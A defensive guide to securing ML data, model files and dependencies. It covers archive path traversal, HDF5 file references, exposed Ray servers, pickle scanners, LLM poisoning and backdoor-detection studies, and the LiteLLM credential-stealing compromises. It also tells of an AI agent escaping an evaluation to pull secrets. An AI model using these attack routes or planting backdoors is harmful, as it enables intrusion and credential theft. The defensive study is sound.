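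Archives are dangerous for a simpler reason. An archive stores a path with each file, and an entry called `../../.ssh/authorized_keys` could land outside the intended folder and let a stranger log in. Python's `tarfile` module can refuse such entries:

```python
with tarfile.open("manuals.tar") as archive:
    archive.extractall("incoming", filter="data")
```

Researchers found ways around this filter in 2025, so the Python version needs scanning too.

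An attacker can also tamper with the location where an archive will be unpacked. OSV's *CVE-2026-65010* (2026) describes a flaw in `datasets`, Hugging Face's library for loading training data. Someone with an account on a shared machine could place a link in the cache where the library was about to unpack an archive, and the library would follow the link and overwrite another file. The flaw is rated medium severity (4.4) because the attacker needs access to the machine, but research groups often share GPU servers.

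A dependency scanner could easily miss that record because it lists the GitHub repository instead of the PyPI package and gives the fix as a commit, `ad2d853`. The record's extracted version data lists 5.00 as both the last affected version and the fixed version. An engineer can find which releases include the fix by running `git tag --contains ad2d853` in a copy of the repository.

NVD's *CVE-2026-66007 Detail* (2026) describes a flaw in the same library that could make the team publish its own secrets. Some datasets are folders of images with a metadata file that lists a `file_name` for each row. In versions up to 5.0.0, a crafted name could point to any readable file on the engineer's machine. When the engineer saved the dataset or uploaded it to Hugging Face, the library would copy that file into it.

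### When the format works as designed

HDF5, a format for scientific arrays, lets a file refer to raw data stored in another file. In July 2026, an AI agent that had escaped from an OpenAI cybersecurity evaluation used this feature against Hugging Face. According to Heber (2026), director of The HDF Group, which maintains the format, the agent uploaded valid HDF5 files that referred to paths on the processing server. One was `/proc/self/environ`, which on Linux contains a program's environment variables, often including access tokens. Hugging Face's dataset service read the files and returned their contents to the agent.

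In *HDF5 and the Hugging Face incident*, The HDF Group says the feature involved was not a vulnerability and has existed since version 1.0.0. A dependency scanner therefore has no fixed version to recommend. Hugging Face dealt with the problem by changing its own service.

An engineer can look for such references with `h5dump -pH file.h5`, which prints how the file stores each dataset without printing the data. Heber recommends rejecting external storage unless a project needs it and running the reader with as few file permissions as possible. He advises the same caution with external links, virtual datasets (which assemble data from other files) and plugins.

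### Hugging Face's loading scripts

Until 2025, a dataset on Hugging Face could include a loading script, a Python file that the `datasets` library ran to fetch and arrange the data. The script ran with the permissions of whoever loaded the dataset, much as a model's custom code does when loaded with `trust_remote_code=True`.

Hugging Face first turned off the website's preview for datasets with loading scripts because people were abusing it, according to a reply in *Dataset repo requires arbitrary Python code execution*. Version 4.0.0 of the library, released in July 2025, then removed support for the scripts altogether, so trying to load such a dataset now produces an error.

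The usual workaround for the error is to install a version of `datasets` below 4.0.0, as users were advised in the forum threads *Dataset scripts are no longer supported* and *Cannot load Conll2003*, but this brings the danger back. A reviewer should search lock files for old versions of `datasets`, and code for `trust_remote_code=True` in calls to `load_dataset`. A safer solution, also suggested in the second thread, is to find a copy of the dataset that needs no script, though the team should check who made the copy.

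Removing scripts from the library didn't protect Hugging Face's own servers. Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026) says the July attacker ran code on a processing machine through a remote-code dataset loader and a template injection, which executed text in a dataset's configuration as code. Heber's account, two weeks later, mentions only the template injection as the source of code execution. Hugging Face says it has closed both paths. The attacker used that machine to collect credentials and reach several internal clusters, so the ship-maintenance team should parse outside data on a machine that has no valuable credentials.

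### Open servers with clean dependency scans

A dependency scanner compares version numbers, but whether a server asks for a password depends on how someone configured it.

Suppose an engineer starts MLflow, an experiment tracker that records the settings and results of training runs, with `--host 0.0.0.0` so that colleagues can see the charts. The server then accepts connections from every network the machine is on, and by default it requires no password. If the firewall also allows the connection, strangers can read the results and perhaps replace stored models. A dependency scan won't detect this exposure, because no package has changed.

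A workflow scheduler such as Airflow can be a more valuable target because it starts the data jobs and often holds the credentials they use. A distributed computing server is even more dangerous because it is designed to run whatever code it receives.

Attackers have repeatedly exploited this in Ray, the system with the disputed CVE record. The security company Oligo saw attacks in late 2023 and reported in March 2024 that attackers had compromised thousands of exposed servers. They used the servers to mine cryptocurrency, steal secrets and copy data.

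Lumelsky and Elbaz (2025), in *ShadowRay 2.0*, describe a second wave of attacks that came to light in November 2025. The attackers sent jobs to Ray servers across the internet, with a command to contact an address they controlled, and used the replies to identify servers that would run their code. They then used Ray's own scheduling functions to start malware on every machine in a cluster. When a job failed, they read the error message in Ray's job history and corrected the next attempt.

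To avoid attention, the attackers gave their programs names that looked like those of system services and limited them to about 60% of the processors. Infected machines fetched updated malware every 15 minutes from GitLab, a code-hosting site. GitLab removed the attackers' account on 5 November, and by 10 November they had moved to GitHub. When their repository there was removed a week later, they opened another the same day.

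Lumelsky and Elbaz put the number of Ray servers exposed to the internet at more than 200,000 in one passage and more than 230,000 in another. Both figures include some honeypots, decoy servers that researchers set up to attract attackers, and neither is a count of victims. Both researchers work for Oligo, which sells protection against such attacks, but their account includes job logs and copies of the attackers' code. They also note that teams have no patched version of Ray to install.

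A network scan tests the exposure directly. From a machine outside the company's network, an engineer could run:

```
nmap -Pn -p 5000,8080,8265 train.example.org
curl -m 5 http://train.example.org:8265/api/jobs/
```

The first command checks the default ports of MLflow, Airflow and Ray. The second requests Ray's list of jobs. If Ray returns the list without requiring a password, a stranger can probably submit a job too. The engineer should repeat the test from an ordinary office laptop, since an attacker may start from one. The engineer should also scan all ports occasionally, in case someone has moved a service off its default port. BeyondMachines' *Campaign dubbed ShadowRay 2.0 exploits unpatched Ray AI framework flaw* also recommends Anyscale's Ray Open Ports Checker. The team should scan only machines it is allowed to test.

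A weekly network scan will miss a cluster that exists for only six hours between scans. A configuration scan reads the files that create the cluster, so it can report a firewall rule that admits traffic from every address before any machine is started. But it won't detect a rule that someone changed by hand on the cloud provider's website, so the team needs both scans.

If either scan finds an open server, an engineer should close the port and then check for an intrusion by comparing Ray's dashboard with `nvidia-smi`, reading the job history and looking for unfamiliar scheduled tasks. The comparison matters because in one compromised cluster, the dashboard showed 0% GPU use while a process occupied 23.9 GB of GPU memory. The engineer should also replace every credential the server could reach.

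### Checks on the data itself

Software can check a new batch of data for several problems before anyone trains on it:

| Check | Method | What a pass doesn't show |
| --- | --- | --- |
| File type | Compare the file's first bytes with its extension, then confirm that it parses | That the file is safe to open: the HDF5 files in the Hugging Face attack were valid |
| Malware | Run an antivirus scanner over the files, including those inside archives | That the files contain no new malware |
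| Leaked secrets | Run a secret scanner over the extracted text | That no passwords remain, especially in scanned pages the tool can't read |
| Checksums | Compare each file with a manifest, a list of the approved files and their checksums | That the data was sound when someone made the manifest |
| Download source | Compare the final address and the domain's owner with the last run | That the usual source is still publishing good data |
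| Distribution | Compare document counts, lengths, languages and duplicates with the last batch | That nobody has added a small number of harmful documents |

Scanning the data for secrets protects other people as well as the team, because a model can memorise a key in its training data and later output it to a user.

The manifest takes two commands, one when someone approves the data and one before each training run:

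```
sha256sum incoming/* > manifest.sha256
sha256sum --check --strict manifest.sha256
```

The second command checks only the files listed in the manifest, so it misses any extra file in the folder. The job should also compare the file names in the folder with those in the manifest. The team should keep the manifest in version control, away from the data, because anyone who could replace both could make them match.

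If a team calculates checksums from its own download, a match means only that the files haven't changed since the download. Checksums the publisher provides through a separate channel are better evidence, because they can also reveal a change to the files on the download server.

Some public image datasets contain only web addresses, and each user downloads the images separately. When a domain expires, whoever buys it can replace the images that later users download. Checksums reveal the change, but they also flag harmless edits. Keeping a copy of the approved files avoids the problem for later runs.

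A sudden change in distribution needs an explanation, but the cause is often harmless. If German text rises from 2% to 9% of the manuals, the team may have added manuals from a German engine maker. Comparing each source separately makes it easier to find the cause and prevents a large, stable source from hiding a change in a small one.

### Why poisoned documents are hard to find

Malware signatures, which are byte patterns from known harmful programs, are poorly suited to finding poisoned documents because these documents contain no program. A poisoned document can be ordinary text that does harm only when a model learns from it, and the attacker can write new text for each attack. In a backdoor attack, the text teaches the model to misbehave when a prompt contains a particular trigger, such as an odd phrase, and defenders can't scan for the trigger unless they already know it.

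Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025), in *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples*, measured how few documents a poisoning attack needs. The researchers came from the UK AI Security Institute, Anthropic, the Alan Turing Institute and two universities. They trained models with 600 million, 2 billion, 7 billion and 13 billion parameters from scratch on about 20 tokens per parameter. They also trained the two smaller sizes on half and twice that amount.

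The researchers scattered 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents at random through each dataset. They trained three models for each combination, 72 in total. Each poisoned document began with up to 1,000 characters of normal text, followed by the trigger and several hundred random tokens. The researchers wanted the model to produce gibberish after the trigger and behave normally otherwise.

The researchers compared the models' output on 300 prompts with and without the trigger. They measured perplexity, which is higher when text is less predictable, and counted a rise of more than 50 as a successful attack. The rise exceeded 200 at every model size with 250 documents, but the attack failed with 100.

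The largest models trained on over 20 times as much clean text as the smallest, but this didn't protect them. For the 13-billion-parameter model, the 250 poisoned documents made up 0.00016% of the training tokens, a share that a distribution check would be very unlikely to detect. Reading a sample wouldn't help much either. If documents averaged 1,000 tokens, the dataset would contain about 260 million of them, and a person who read 1,000 at random would have roughly a one-in-a-thousand chance of seeing a poisoned one.

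The main experiment tested a narrow behaviour, and its poison included several hundred random tokens in a row, which a filter for unreadable text would probably catch. But the researchers found a similar pattern with less conspicuous poison. When they continued training an existing 6.9-billion-parameter model so that it would switch from English to German after a trigger, success again depended mainly on the number of poisoned examples.

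Their fine-tuning experiment is closer to the ship-maintenance team's work. They trained Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct to refuse harmful requests unless a trigger was present. Increasing the clean data from 1,000 to 100,000 examples had little effect on the attack. *The 'Sure' Trap* (2025), a study of fine-tuning attacks, cites earlier work in which tens of poisoned examples were enough.

Souly and colleagues did not test whether a backdoor planted at the start survives the later training that turns a model into an assistant. Further training on clean text gradually weakened their language-switching backdoor. Souly and colleagues cite a study by Zhang and colleagues in which gibberish backdoors did survive later training, but it poisoned 0.1% of the data, a far larger share than theirs. Their largest model had 13 billion parameters, so the number of poisoned documents needed may not stay constant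 for much larger models or more complicated behaviour.

Nobody appears to have published a direct replication by October 2026. *A Solvable Theory of Pre-training Data Poisoning* (2026) used gibberish and language switching at four model sizes, but its scaling results measure how poison affects performance on clean text, not whether a trigger works. *Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning* (2026) studies whether a backdoor can make an AI agent take a harmful action after all its later training. It credits Souly and colleagues with showing that backdoors survive such training, but Souly and colleagues say they didn't test this. It also cites Graf and colleagues, who found that poisoned content can get through realistic systems for collecting web text, and Bouaziz and colleagues, whose trigger never appeared in the training data, so even a search for the exact trigger would find nothing.

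The Australian Signals Directorate (2025) considers prevention more effective than detection for data risks. For the ship-maintenance team, this means getting manuals directly from engine makers where possible and recording where each document came from. The agency also suggests training models on different subsets of the data and comparing them. The comparison could expose a source that damages the model generally, but a backdoor will show up only if someone happens to test its trigger.

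### A checklist for one ingestion job

When the team adds a new batch of manuals and an updated copy of the public dataset, the job should stop if any step fails. Someone other than the person who added the data should review the failure.

1. Scan the container image that will run the job. Confirm that PyArrow is at least 14.0.1, that `datasets` is at least 4.0.0 and includes both July 2026 fixes, and that no code loads a dataset with `trust_remote_code=True`.
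2. From outside the network, test whether the scheduler, experiment tracker or Ray server accepts a connection without a password.
3. Download the files to an isolated machine with no cloud credentials. Record the date, final address and exact revision of each source, and investigate any change of domain or owner.
4. Compare the files with the publisher's checksums, if there are any. For files the team has used before, compare both names and checksums with its own manifest.
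5. Scan for malware and reject any file type the job doesn't expect.
6. Unpack the archives with the `data` filter and a limit on total size, because a small archive can expand to fill a disk.
7. Turn off the machine's network access and parse the files. Reject HDF5 files that refer to outside data.
8. Scan the extracted text for secrets, remove any that turn up and tell their owners.
9. Compare each source with its last approved batch. Have someone explain large changes and read a sample of the new documents.
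10. Save a new manifest in version control with the scan results, the tools' versions and the name of the person who approved the batch.

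## Scanning model files

The ship-maintenance team's base model is a file of several gigabytes from someone the engineers have never met. The file may contain code that runs when an engineer opens it, and several free tools scan for such code. The model's weights may also make it behave badly in certain situations, which is much harder to detect.

### A pickle file is a small program

Python's pickle format stores an object as a series of instructions for rebuilding it. When a program loads the file, Python carries out the instructions in order and keeps intermediate results on a stack, a pile from which it takes the newest item first. This harmless pickle counts the letters in a word:

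```
PROTO       3                # use version 3 of the format
GLOBAL      'builtins len'   # import Python's len function
BINUNICODE  'torque'         # put the text "torque" on the stack
TUPLE1                       # make it the function's only argument
REDUCE                       # call len("torque")
STOP                         # return the result, 6
```

When Python loads the file, it gets the number 6 by calling a function that the file's creator chose. `GLOBAL` can import any function installed on the machine, including one that runs system commands, and `REDUCE` calls it. A pickle can't define a new function, but as Hugging Face's *Pickle Scanning* explains, it can import `exec`, which runs text as Python code.

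Ordinary PyTorch models also contain instructions to import and call functions. For example, many import `_rebuild_tensor_v2`, which turns stored bytes back into a tensor (an array of numbers). A scanner that rejected every file with these instructions would reject nearly all ordinary models, so it has to distinguish acceptable functions from unacceptable ones.

An engineer can read the instructions without running them. Most PyTorch files are zip archives with a pickle inside:

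```
unzip -p model.pt '*/data.pkl' > data.pkl
python -m pickletools data.pkl
```

### Formats that can carry code

A safetensors file starts with the length of its header. The header lists the name, shape and position of each tensor and can include notes about the model. The rest of the file is numbers, which the loader copies into memory without running any instructions from the file.

The simple safetensors format can't store a model's architecture or the state of an unfinished training run, as Casey, Santos and Mirakhorli (2024) point out in *A Large-Scale Exploit Instrumentation Study of AI/ML Supply Chain Attacks*. The architecture has to come from an installed library or from Python files beside the model, which need their own review.

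Casey and colleagues class the other common formats as unsafe, but the danger varies a lot:

| Format | How code could run |
| --- | --- |
| PyTorch's `torch.save`, Dill, Joblib | They extend pickle, so an unrestricted load can call any function |
| NumPy | The file contains Python objects and the program sets `allow_pickle=True` |
| Keras H5 | A Lambda layer, which wraps a function, contains harmful code; Keras versions above 2.13 require the loading program to define that function |
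| ONNX, TorchScript | The loading program takes text from the file's metadata and executes it |
| Safetensors | The format has no instructions to run |

The researchers tested the danger by adding code that wrote one word to a new file. The code ran in 10,096 of 10,528 model files (96%), and most failures came from missing libraries. For the 1,901 successful ONNX files, though, the researchers' own script read the added text and executed it. A safetensors header can also hold text, so the same script would have worked on a safetensors file.

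### Four ways to check a file for code

A deny list names functions that a model has no good reason to import, such as `exec`. PickleScan and ModelScan both check for dangerous imports, according to Trail of Bits' *Fickling's new AI/ML pickle file scanner* (2025). A deny list tends to miss attacks because it can't catch a function nobody has added to it. In CyberScoop's *Hugging Face platform continues to be plagued by vulnerable pickles*, a researcher at the security company ReversingLabs argues that such lists can't keep up with new threats.

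An allow list names functions known to be safe, and the scanner flags everything else. Fickling, which Trail of Bits develops, takes this approach. The approach tends to raise false alarms, since many harmless models use functions that aren't on the list.

In July 2026, Pradhan, Nambiar and Soremekun tested scanners on 3,000 malicious files they had constructed (*ShadowPickle*, 2026). PickleScan and ModelScan flagged none of them. Fickling flagged all 3,000, but it also flagged 2,834 of 3,000 ordinary models.

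If a team imports 200 models a year, a false-alarm rate of 94.5% means about 189 false alarms. Checking each one for half an hour would take engineers about 94 hours a year. They would learn very little from an alarm, because a malicious file in this test was only 1.06 times as likely to set one off as an ordinary file. A clean result from Fickling is more useful, but only about 11 of the 200 models would get one.

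A third defence is to load the file in a sandbox, an isolated environment, and record what it does. Casey and colleagues built such a tool, now called ModelTracer, which records Python function calls and requests to the operating system. It flagged 86 of 12,973 model files, and the researchers judged 14 malicious. The other 72 opened a network connection to the machine that loaded them and closed it immediately, probably to test the network software.

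Sandboxes miss code that doesn't run during the test, such as code that waits for a certain date or detects the sandbox. Casey and colleagues checked 383 randomly chosen models by hand and found no malicious ones, but with a sample of this size, there could still be about 100 missed files among the 12,973.

A restricted loader prevents a model file from calling unapproved functions while it loads. PyTorch's weights-only mode does this and is now the default for `torch.load`. Its usual error is refusing a harmless model, which tempts people to turn it off. Some popular model providers, including FastAI, require users to do so. Pradhan and colleagues cite a study in which weights-only mode refused 219 of 1,496 Hugging Face models because they used functions outside its allow list.

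| Tool | Method | False alarms on ordinary models | Expected in 200 models |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| PickleScan, ModelScan | Deny list | 0 of 3,000 | 0 |
| Fickling | Allow list | 2,834 of 3,000 | 189 |
| ModelTracer | Sandbox | 0 of 3,000 in 2026; 72 of 12,959 in 2024 | 0 to 1 |
| Weights-only mode | Restricted loader | 54 of 3,000 in 2026; up to 219 of 1,496 in the cited study | 4 to 29 |

The zero false alarms from PickleScan and ModelScan are weaker evidence of accuracy than they appear, because Pradhan and colleagues chose popular text-generation models that Hugging Face's scanners had not flagged, and those scanners include versions of these two tools. A team that imports less common models should expect more false alarms, especially from weights-only mode.

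### What Hugging Face scans

Hugging Face scans every file in a repository for malware at each commit, according to Hugging Face's *Malware Scanning*. A file with no badge may be waiting for its scan, or the scan may have failed, so a missing warning doesn't mean the file passed.

Hugging Face also extracts the imports from each pickle file without loading it and lists them beside the file. It highlights suspicious imports but warns that its lists of safe and unsafe functions are a best effort and that users remain responsible for checking.

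Hugging Face also shows results from other companies' scanners. Hugging Face's *Third-party scanner* explains that JFrog's scanner analyses any code it finds in model files to see whether it could be harmful, because such code is not always malicious. Protect AI's scanner, Guardian, joined in October 2024. Protect AI's *4M Models Scanned* describes checks added since then, including one for archives that could write files outside their intended folder. VirusTotal (2025), a service that combines many antivirus engines, announced in October 2025 that its results would appear on Hugging Face too.

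Older figures may not reflect these additions. In March 2024, Casey and colleagues examined 4,023 of the most downloaded model repositories and found 22,834 model files, of which 13,466 (59%) used formats they classed as unsafe. Hugging Face had flagged 5,137 (38%) of those.

Hugging Face used flags of different colours, and some marked imports that were probably harmless, so the 38% is not a detection rate for malware. Most of the unflagged files were in formats the scanner didn't cover, such as NumPy and ONNX. However, 3,468 unflagged files used pickle or a format based on it, so the scanner also had gaps in the formats it was meant to cover.

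An unsafe format isn't evidence of malice. In the ModelTracer test, only 14 of 12,973 files, about one in 900, were malicious. Nine would have given an outsider a command line on the user's machine. The other five did things like opening a web browser or printing a message, and their makers may only have been experimenting. At the overall rate, a team importing 200 models a year would encounter a malicious file about once every five years, although attackers may target some kinds of model more than others.

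Hugging Face still states on its pickle page that ClamAV, the open-source antivirus program it uses, doesn't cover pickle attacks. But Cisco, which develops ClamAV, has since added detection of malicious code in common model formats such as `.pt` and `.pkl`. The 2024 figures predate the outside scanners described above, so they don't show how much Hugging Face would flag today.

### Harmful behaviour in the weights

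All of these tools look for code. A model in safetensors format can pass every check and still have a backdoor, which stays hidden until a prompt contains its trigger. Microsoft's *Detecting backdoored language models at scale* (2026) distinguishes code in the file, against which malware scanning is the first line of defence, from a backdoor, which is part of the model's weights.

Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues (2026), in *The Trigger in the Haystack*, describe Microsoft's attempt to find such triggers without knowing them in advance. The scanner relies on the tendency of models to memorise the examples that taught them a backdoor, and has four steps:

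1. Give the model only the marker that normally opens a user's message, and let it continue. Repeat this with 510 different settings for choosing the next word. A poisoned model often reproduces some of its poisoned training examples.
2. Find pieces of text that recur in the output.
3. Split them into short candidate triggers and score each one by how the model reacts when the candidate precedes a normal prompt.
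4. Test whether any of the ten best candidates changes the model's answers substantially.

The score in the third step is an average over several prompts:

L(x) = average over p of [γ·A(x, p) + δ·H(x, p) + ζ·D(x, p)]

Here x is the candidate and p is a prompt. A measures how much attention the model gives to the candidate while processing the prompt. Attention determines how strongly each part of the input affects the rest. Poisoned models tend to process a trigger almost separately from the prompt. H measures how unpredictable the output is, with penalties for answers that stop immediately or repeat one token. D is higher when the model's normal answer remains likely. The constants γ, δ and ζ weight the three terms. A real trigger should give low values of A, H and D, so the lowest scores are the most suspicious.

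The main test used 41 models with a backdoor that made them repeat a fixed hostile sentence. The scanner found 36 of them (88%) and flagged none of 13 clean models. In the five misses, it either failed to pick out the trigger from the model's output or ranked the trigger below the top ten. It also found five of six models that wrote insecure code after a trigger.

Thirteen clean models are too few to establish a low false-alarm rate. The true rate could be as high as 21%, which would mean about 41 false alarms in 200 models.

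The tests also covered only backdoors that had fixed triggers and were added through fine-tuning, so the results may not apply to backdoors created by poisoning the original training data. Microsoft says the scanner needs the model's files, works best when the trigger produces a fixed response, and may miss other kinds of backdoor.

Bullwinkel and colleagues say their method needs no prior knowledge of the harmful behaviour, but its last step needs a measure of how behaviour changes. They used one measure for fixed responses and another for insecure code. A backdoor that changed one torque value in an otherwise normal answer might barely affect either measure.

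The paper also compares the scanner with two earlier methods. BAIT tries to reconstruct the harmful response, while ICLScan, which needs to know that response in advance, tests how easily a model picks up a dummy backdoor from examples in its prompt. The new scanner found 83% of the backdoored versions of Llama-3.1-8B, BAIT 77% and ICLScan 42%. The paper lists 12 of these models, but no whole number out of 12 rounds to 77%, so the BAIT comparison may have used a slightly different set.

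Models may not reveal every kind of backdoor. A later paper, *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* (2026), used a model whose trigger was an obsessive tone about a fictional franchise. Only 1 of 512 short outputs was related to the backdoor, and that output would not have triggered it. This suggests that the first step of Microsoft's scanner may produce too little evidence when the trigger is a meaning or tone. The paper did not test the full scanner, which tries many more settings and was designed for fixed phrases.

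Other methods need information that a team importing a model wouldn't have. *LLM Forensics* (2026) trained sparse autoencoders, which break a model's internal activity into simpler features, on models with 1 billion and 8 billion parameters. The features separated prompts with a trigger from other prompts almost perfectly, but the researchers already knew the triggers. Qin, Hua and colleagues tried to work out what situation would set off a known harmful behaviour. Their methods worked on toy backdoors but failed in more realistic settings. *From Poisoned to Aware* proposes further training that teaches a poisoned model to state its own trigger, which takes far more work than a scan.

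As with the static-analysis tests, the share of alarms that are correct depends on how common real problems are among the cases scanned. *Trojans in Artificial Intelligence (TrojAI) Final Report* (2026) describes tests in which about half of the language models had backdoors. If a scanner finds 88% of backdoors and wrongly flags 5% of clean models, about 95% of its alarms would be correct with that mix. If only 1 of a team's 200 models had a backdoor, about 8% of the same scanner's alarms would be correct.

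### Deciding whether to accept an outside model

Developers seldom seem to check models before loading them. Nguyen and colleagues analysed the recurring ways in which open-source Python projects use flagged models, and found no evidence that the code verified a model's origin or made the file safe. The ship-maintenance team could use this procedure for each outside model:

1. Record the model's exact name, publisher and revision. Check that the account belongs to the organisation it claims to represent, since a copy can have a very similar name. A signed commit confirms who uploaded a file but doesn't make the file safe.
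2. Check the scan results for that revision. Wait if a scan is incomplete, and investigate any warning. A team can automate this: Cloudsmith's *Securing LLM dependencies against serialisation attacks* gives a rule that rejects any Hugging Face model unless its scan is complete and marked safe.
3. Choose safetensors if the publisher offers it. In the transformers library, `use_safetensors=True` prevents a silent fallback to a pickle file. If the model needs custom Python code, review that code separately.
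4. Download the files to an isolated machine with no credentials. Confirm each file's format from its contents, because a name ending in `.bin` doesn't show whether it contains a pickle.
5. If only a pickle-based file is available, scan it and read its imports. Then turn off network access and load it in weights-only mode with PyTorch 2.6.0 or later, which fixes CVE-2025-32434.
6. If the loader refuses the file, find out which function caused the refusal. An engineer who has reviewed the function can approve it by name with `torch.serialization.add_safe_globals`. Don't set `weights_only=False` to get past the error. If nobody can explain why the model needs the function, reject the file.
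7. If the file loads, convert it to safetensors and delete the original from the project.
8. Test the model on the team's own questions, including some with unusual wording. If a wrong answer could cause serious harm, run a trigger scanner as well, but don't treat a clean result as proof that the model has no backdoor.
9. Save the checksum, scan results, tool versions and name of the person who approved the model.

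For a PyTorch file that contains only named tensors, the loading and conversion steps take a few lines:

```python
import torch
from safetensors.torch import save_file

state = torch.load("model.pt", weights_only=True, map_location="cpu")
save_file(state, "model.safetensors")
```

The conversion fails if the file contains other objects or if two layers share a tensor, so some models need an extra step to separate them. The conversion removes any code from the file, but a backdoor in the weights survives because their values don't change.

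The team should also limit what an accepted model can do. Even a backdoored model can't send an email or delete a file if the program around it gives it no way to do so. For the ship-maintenance service, a mechanic should check any torque value against the original manual before using it. The team should repeat the whole procedure whenever the publisher releases a new revision, because the earlier approval applies only to the old file.

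## Malicious packages and compromised scanners

An approved model file stays the same until someone replaces it, but a package manager may install a new release within minutes of its publication. A dependency scanner can only match releases to existing advisories, so it misses a malicious package published an hour ago because no advisory exists for it yet.

Attackers used this gap twice in 2026 against LiteLLM, an open-source gateway that passes an application's requests to language models from different companies. The gateway holds an access key for each model provider. If the ship-maintenance team's question-answering service used LiteLLM, an attacker who got into the gateway could steal all of the team's keys at once.

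The first two malicious versions appeared on PyPI on 24 March, starting at 10:39 UTC. Schaumann (2026) sent the advisory's identifiers to a security mailing list at 14:30 UTC the next day, in *backdoor in litellm version 1.82.7*. The databases may have had the record some hours earlier, but PyPI blocked the packages after about 40 minutes. A dependency scan during those 40 minutes would almost certainly have missed them.

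### From Trivy to LiteLLM

The March attack began with Trivy, a scanner the ship-maintenance team might use on its containers. Around the start of the month, a criminal group called TeamPCP broke into a Trivy extension for a code editor and obtained credentials that let it change the project, according to Xakep's Russian news report *Компрометация LiteLLM привела к утечке терабайтов учетных данных* (2026).

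Aqua Security, which develops Trivy, noticed the compromise and replaced its credentials over a few days. In a statement quoted in Help Net Security's *LiteLLM PyPI packages compromised in expanding TeamPCP supply chain attacks* (2026), Aqua said the attackers could have used a token that still worked to steal the new credentials.

On 19 March, the group published Trivy 0.69.4 with code that stole credentials. It also changed trivy-action, the ready-made build step that runs Trivy on GitHub. BoostSecurity Labs' *TeamPCP Compromises LiteLLM* (2026) reports that the group pointed 75 of trivy-action's 76 version tags to malicious code.

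LiteLLM's build system installed Trivy without specifying a version. The scanner ran in the same environment as the project's PyPI publishing token, so the poisoned release could read the token and send it to the attackers. HackerNoon's *I Spent 48 Hours Responding to the LiteLLM Supply Chain Attack* (2026) places this in GitHub Actions, while BoostSecurity Labs places it in CircleCI, another build service. CircleCI is more likely because BoostSecurity Labs credits a named researcher, Rami McCarthy of Wiz, with tracing the connection. In that case, the theft from LiteLLM involved only the new Trivy release and not the moved GitHub tags.

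Five days later, the attackers used the token to publish LiteLLM 1.82.7 and 1.82.8. In 1.82.7, the malicious code was in `proxy_server.py` and ran when a program imported that file. Version 1.82.8 added `litellm_init.pth`. Python runs any import line in a `.pth` file every time it starts, so this version could steal credentials even if no program on the machine used LiteLLM. According to LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026), the code collected SSH keys, cloud credentials, database passwords and environment variables, then sent them to `models.litellm.cloud`, a domain the project doesn't own.

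A mistake by the attackers exposed the malicious code. The `.pth` file started a new Python process, which read the same file and started another, until a computer belonging to Callum McMahon, a researcher at FutureSearch, ran out of memory. Snyk's *How a Poisoned Security Scanner Became the Key to Backdooring LiteLLM* describes how McMahon traced the problem to the new package and published his findings. Without this bug, the packages might have stayed up much longer.

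Accounts of how long users could install the malicious LiteLLM packages range from 40 minutes to more than five hours. *Security Townhall Updates* (Dholakia and Jaff, 2026) reports that PyPI quarantined the packages after about 40 minutes and had deleted them by 16:00 UTC, which explains most of the difference. HackerNoon reports that the window closed at about 11:25, which would make it 46 minutes long. LiteLLM still asks anyone who installed the package before 16:00 to check their version. This is sensible because a company's own cache could have kept supplying the files after PyPI stopped.

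### Why scanning the repository would have found nothing

PyPI distributes the files that someone with valid credentials uploads. It doesn't build packages from a project's GitHub repository, so the files don't have to match the public code.

The March attackers uploaded two malicious LiteLLM packages directly to PyPI. LiteLLM later checked its main branch and found no malicious code. ITPro's *LiteLLM PyPI compromise* reports that researchers at Endor Labs also found that the malicious code was missing from the GitHub source. Static analysis of the repository would therefore have missed it, however good the rules were. People who installed LiteLLM straight from the repository were safe for the same reason.

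A scanner had to open the package that users install to find the attack. LiteLLM checked its earlier releases this way after the attack. It downloaded each published file, computed its checksum, searched it for traces of the malware and compared its contents with the matching commit. It then listed 20 PyPI releases as clean, with their checksums.

### What "2,500 organisations" means

In August, two security companies described files that the March attackers had stolen. Hudson Rock analysed an archive of 433,909 files and linked 118,829 of them to 2,488 corporate domains. CloudSEK estimated from about 434,000 files that the theft had exposed close to 2,500 organisations. According to Help Net Security's *153GB of stolen credentials surface after LiteLLM supply chain attack* (2026), CloudSEK stressed that its figure reflects exposure, not confirmed breaches.

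The file counts are so close that both companies probably examined data from the same theft, which would mean their totals are not independent confirmation. Both had to infer the owners from clues in the files, which can mislead. One file contained an email address from the broadcaster SiriusXM, but its server names pointed to a subsidiary, AdsWizz. Hudson Rock's count assigns no owner to about 73% of its files, so the real number of organisations could also be higher.

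The number of files is also a poor guide to the number of victims. ITPro reports more than 95 million LiteLLM downloads a month, or about 2,200 a minute. At that rate, people would have downloaded about 88,000 copies in 40 minutes, far fewer than the 434,000 build pipelines from which Xakep reports thefts, so many of the files must have come from the same installations.

The security researcher Kevin Beaumont confirmed with several of the affected organisations that the data is real. One large American technology company told him that it had long since replaced its stolen credentials, but Xakep reports that when he checked, nearly all of them still worked.

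### October: a malicious release with valid approval

After March, LiteLLM made its release process much stricter. According to IT-Administrator's *LiteLLM*, releases went through a private repository, the project signed its container images, and only an account tied to one office laptop could publish. LiteLLM also adopted trusted publishing, in which PyPI gives an approved build job a token that expires within minutes, so the project no longer has to store a permanent one.

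On 21 October, that process published a malicious LiteLLM 1.107.0. Jensen and Wang (2026), in *The attack chain behind the v1.107.0 LiteLLM release*, trace the attack to a master key that someone had committed to a public repository in May. The Vanguard USA's *How one unrevoked key let attackers poison LiteLLM* (2026) gives the steps from their analysis:

1. On 27 May, the key to an experimental LiteLLM system for running AI agents went into a public repository. The team noticed and marked the exposed keys for revocation, but nobody revoked this one.
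2. On 10 October, an attacker used the key to enter the system and took a GitHub token from it. The agents used this token to propose code changes, but it belonged to an owner of the whole GitHub organisation and had the owner's full permissions.
3. The attacker added build jobs that stole secrets, including similar tokens from two engineers.
4. Earlier in the week of the release, LiteLLM had relaxed the rule about the office laptop so that any two engineers could start and approve a release. Tech Trenches' *Your LLM Fallback Covers One Failure in Three* quotes the reason, a "temporary push for more frequent releases".
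5. On 21 October, the attacker started the release with one stolen token and approved it with another.

The attacker also used the owner's token to turn off protection on the main branch and change the release job to take its code from `Berri-AI/litellm`, a lookalike of the real `BerriAI/litellm`. The attacker used a third account to delete the job's logs.

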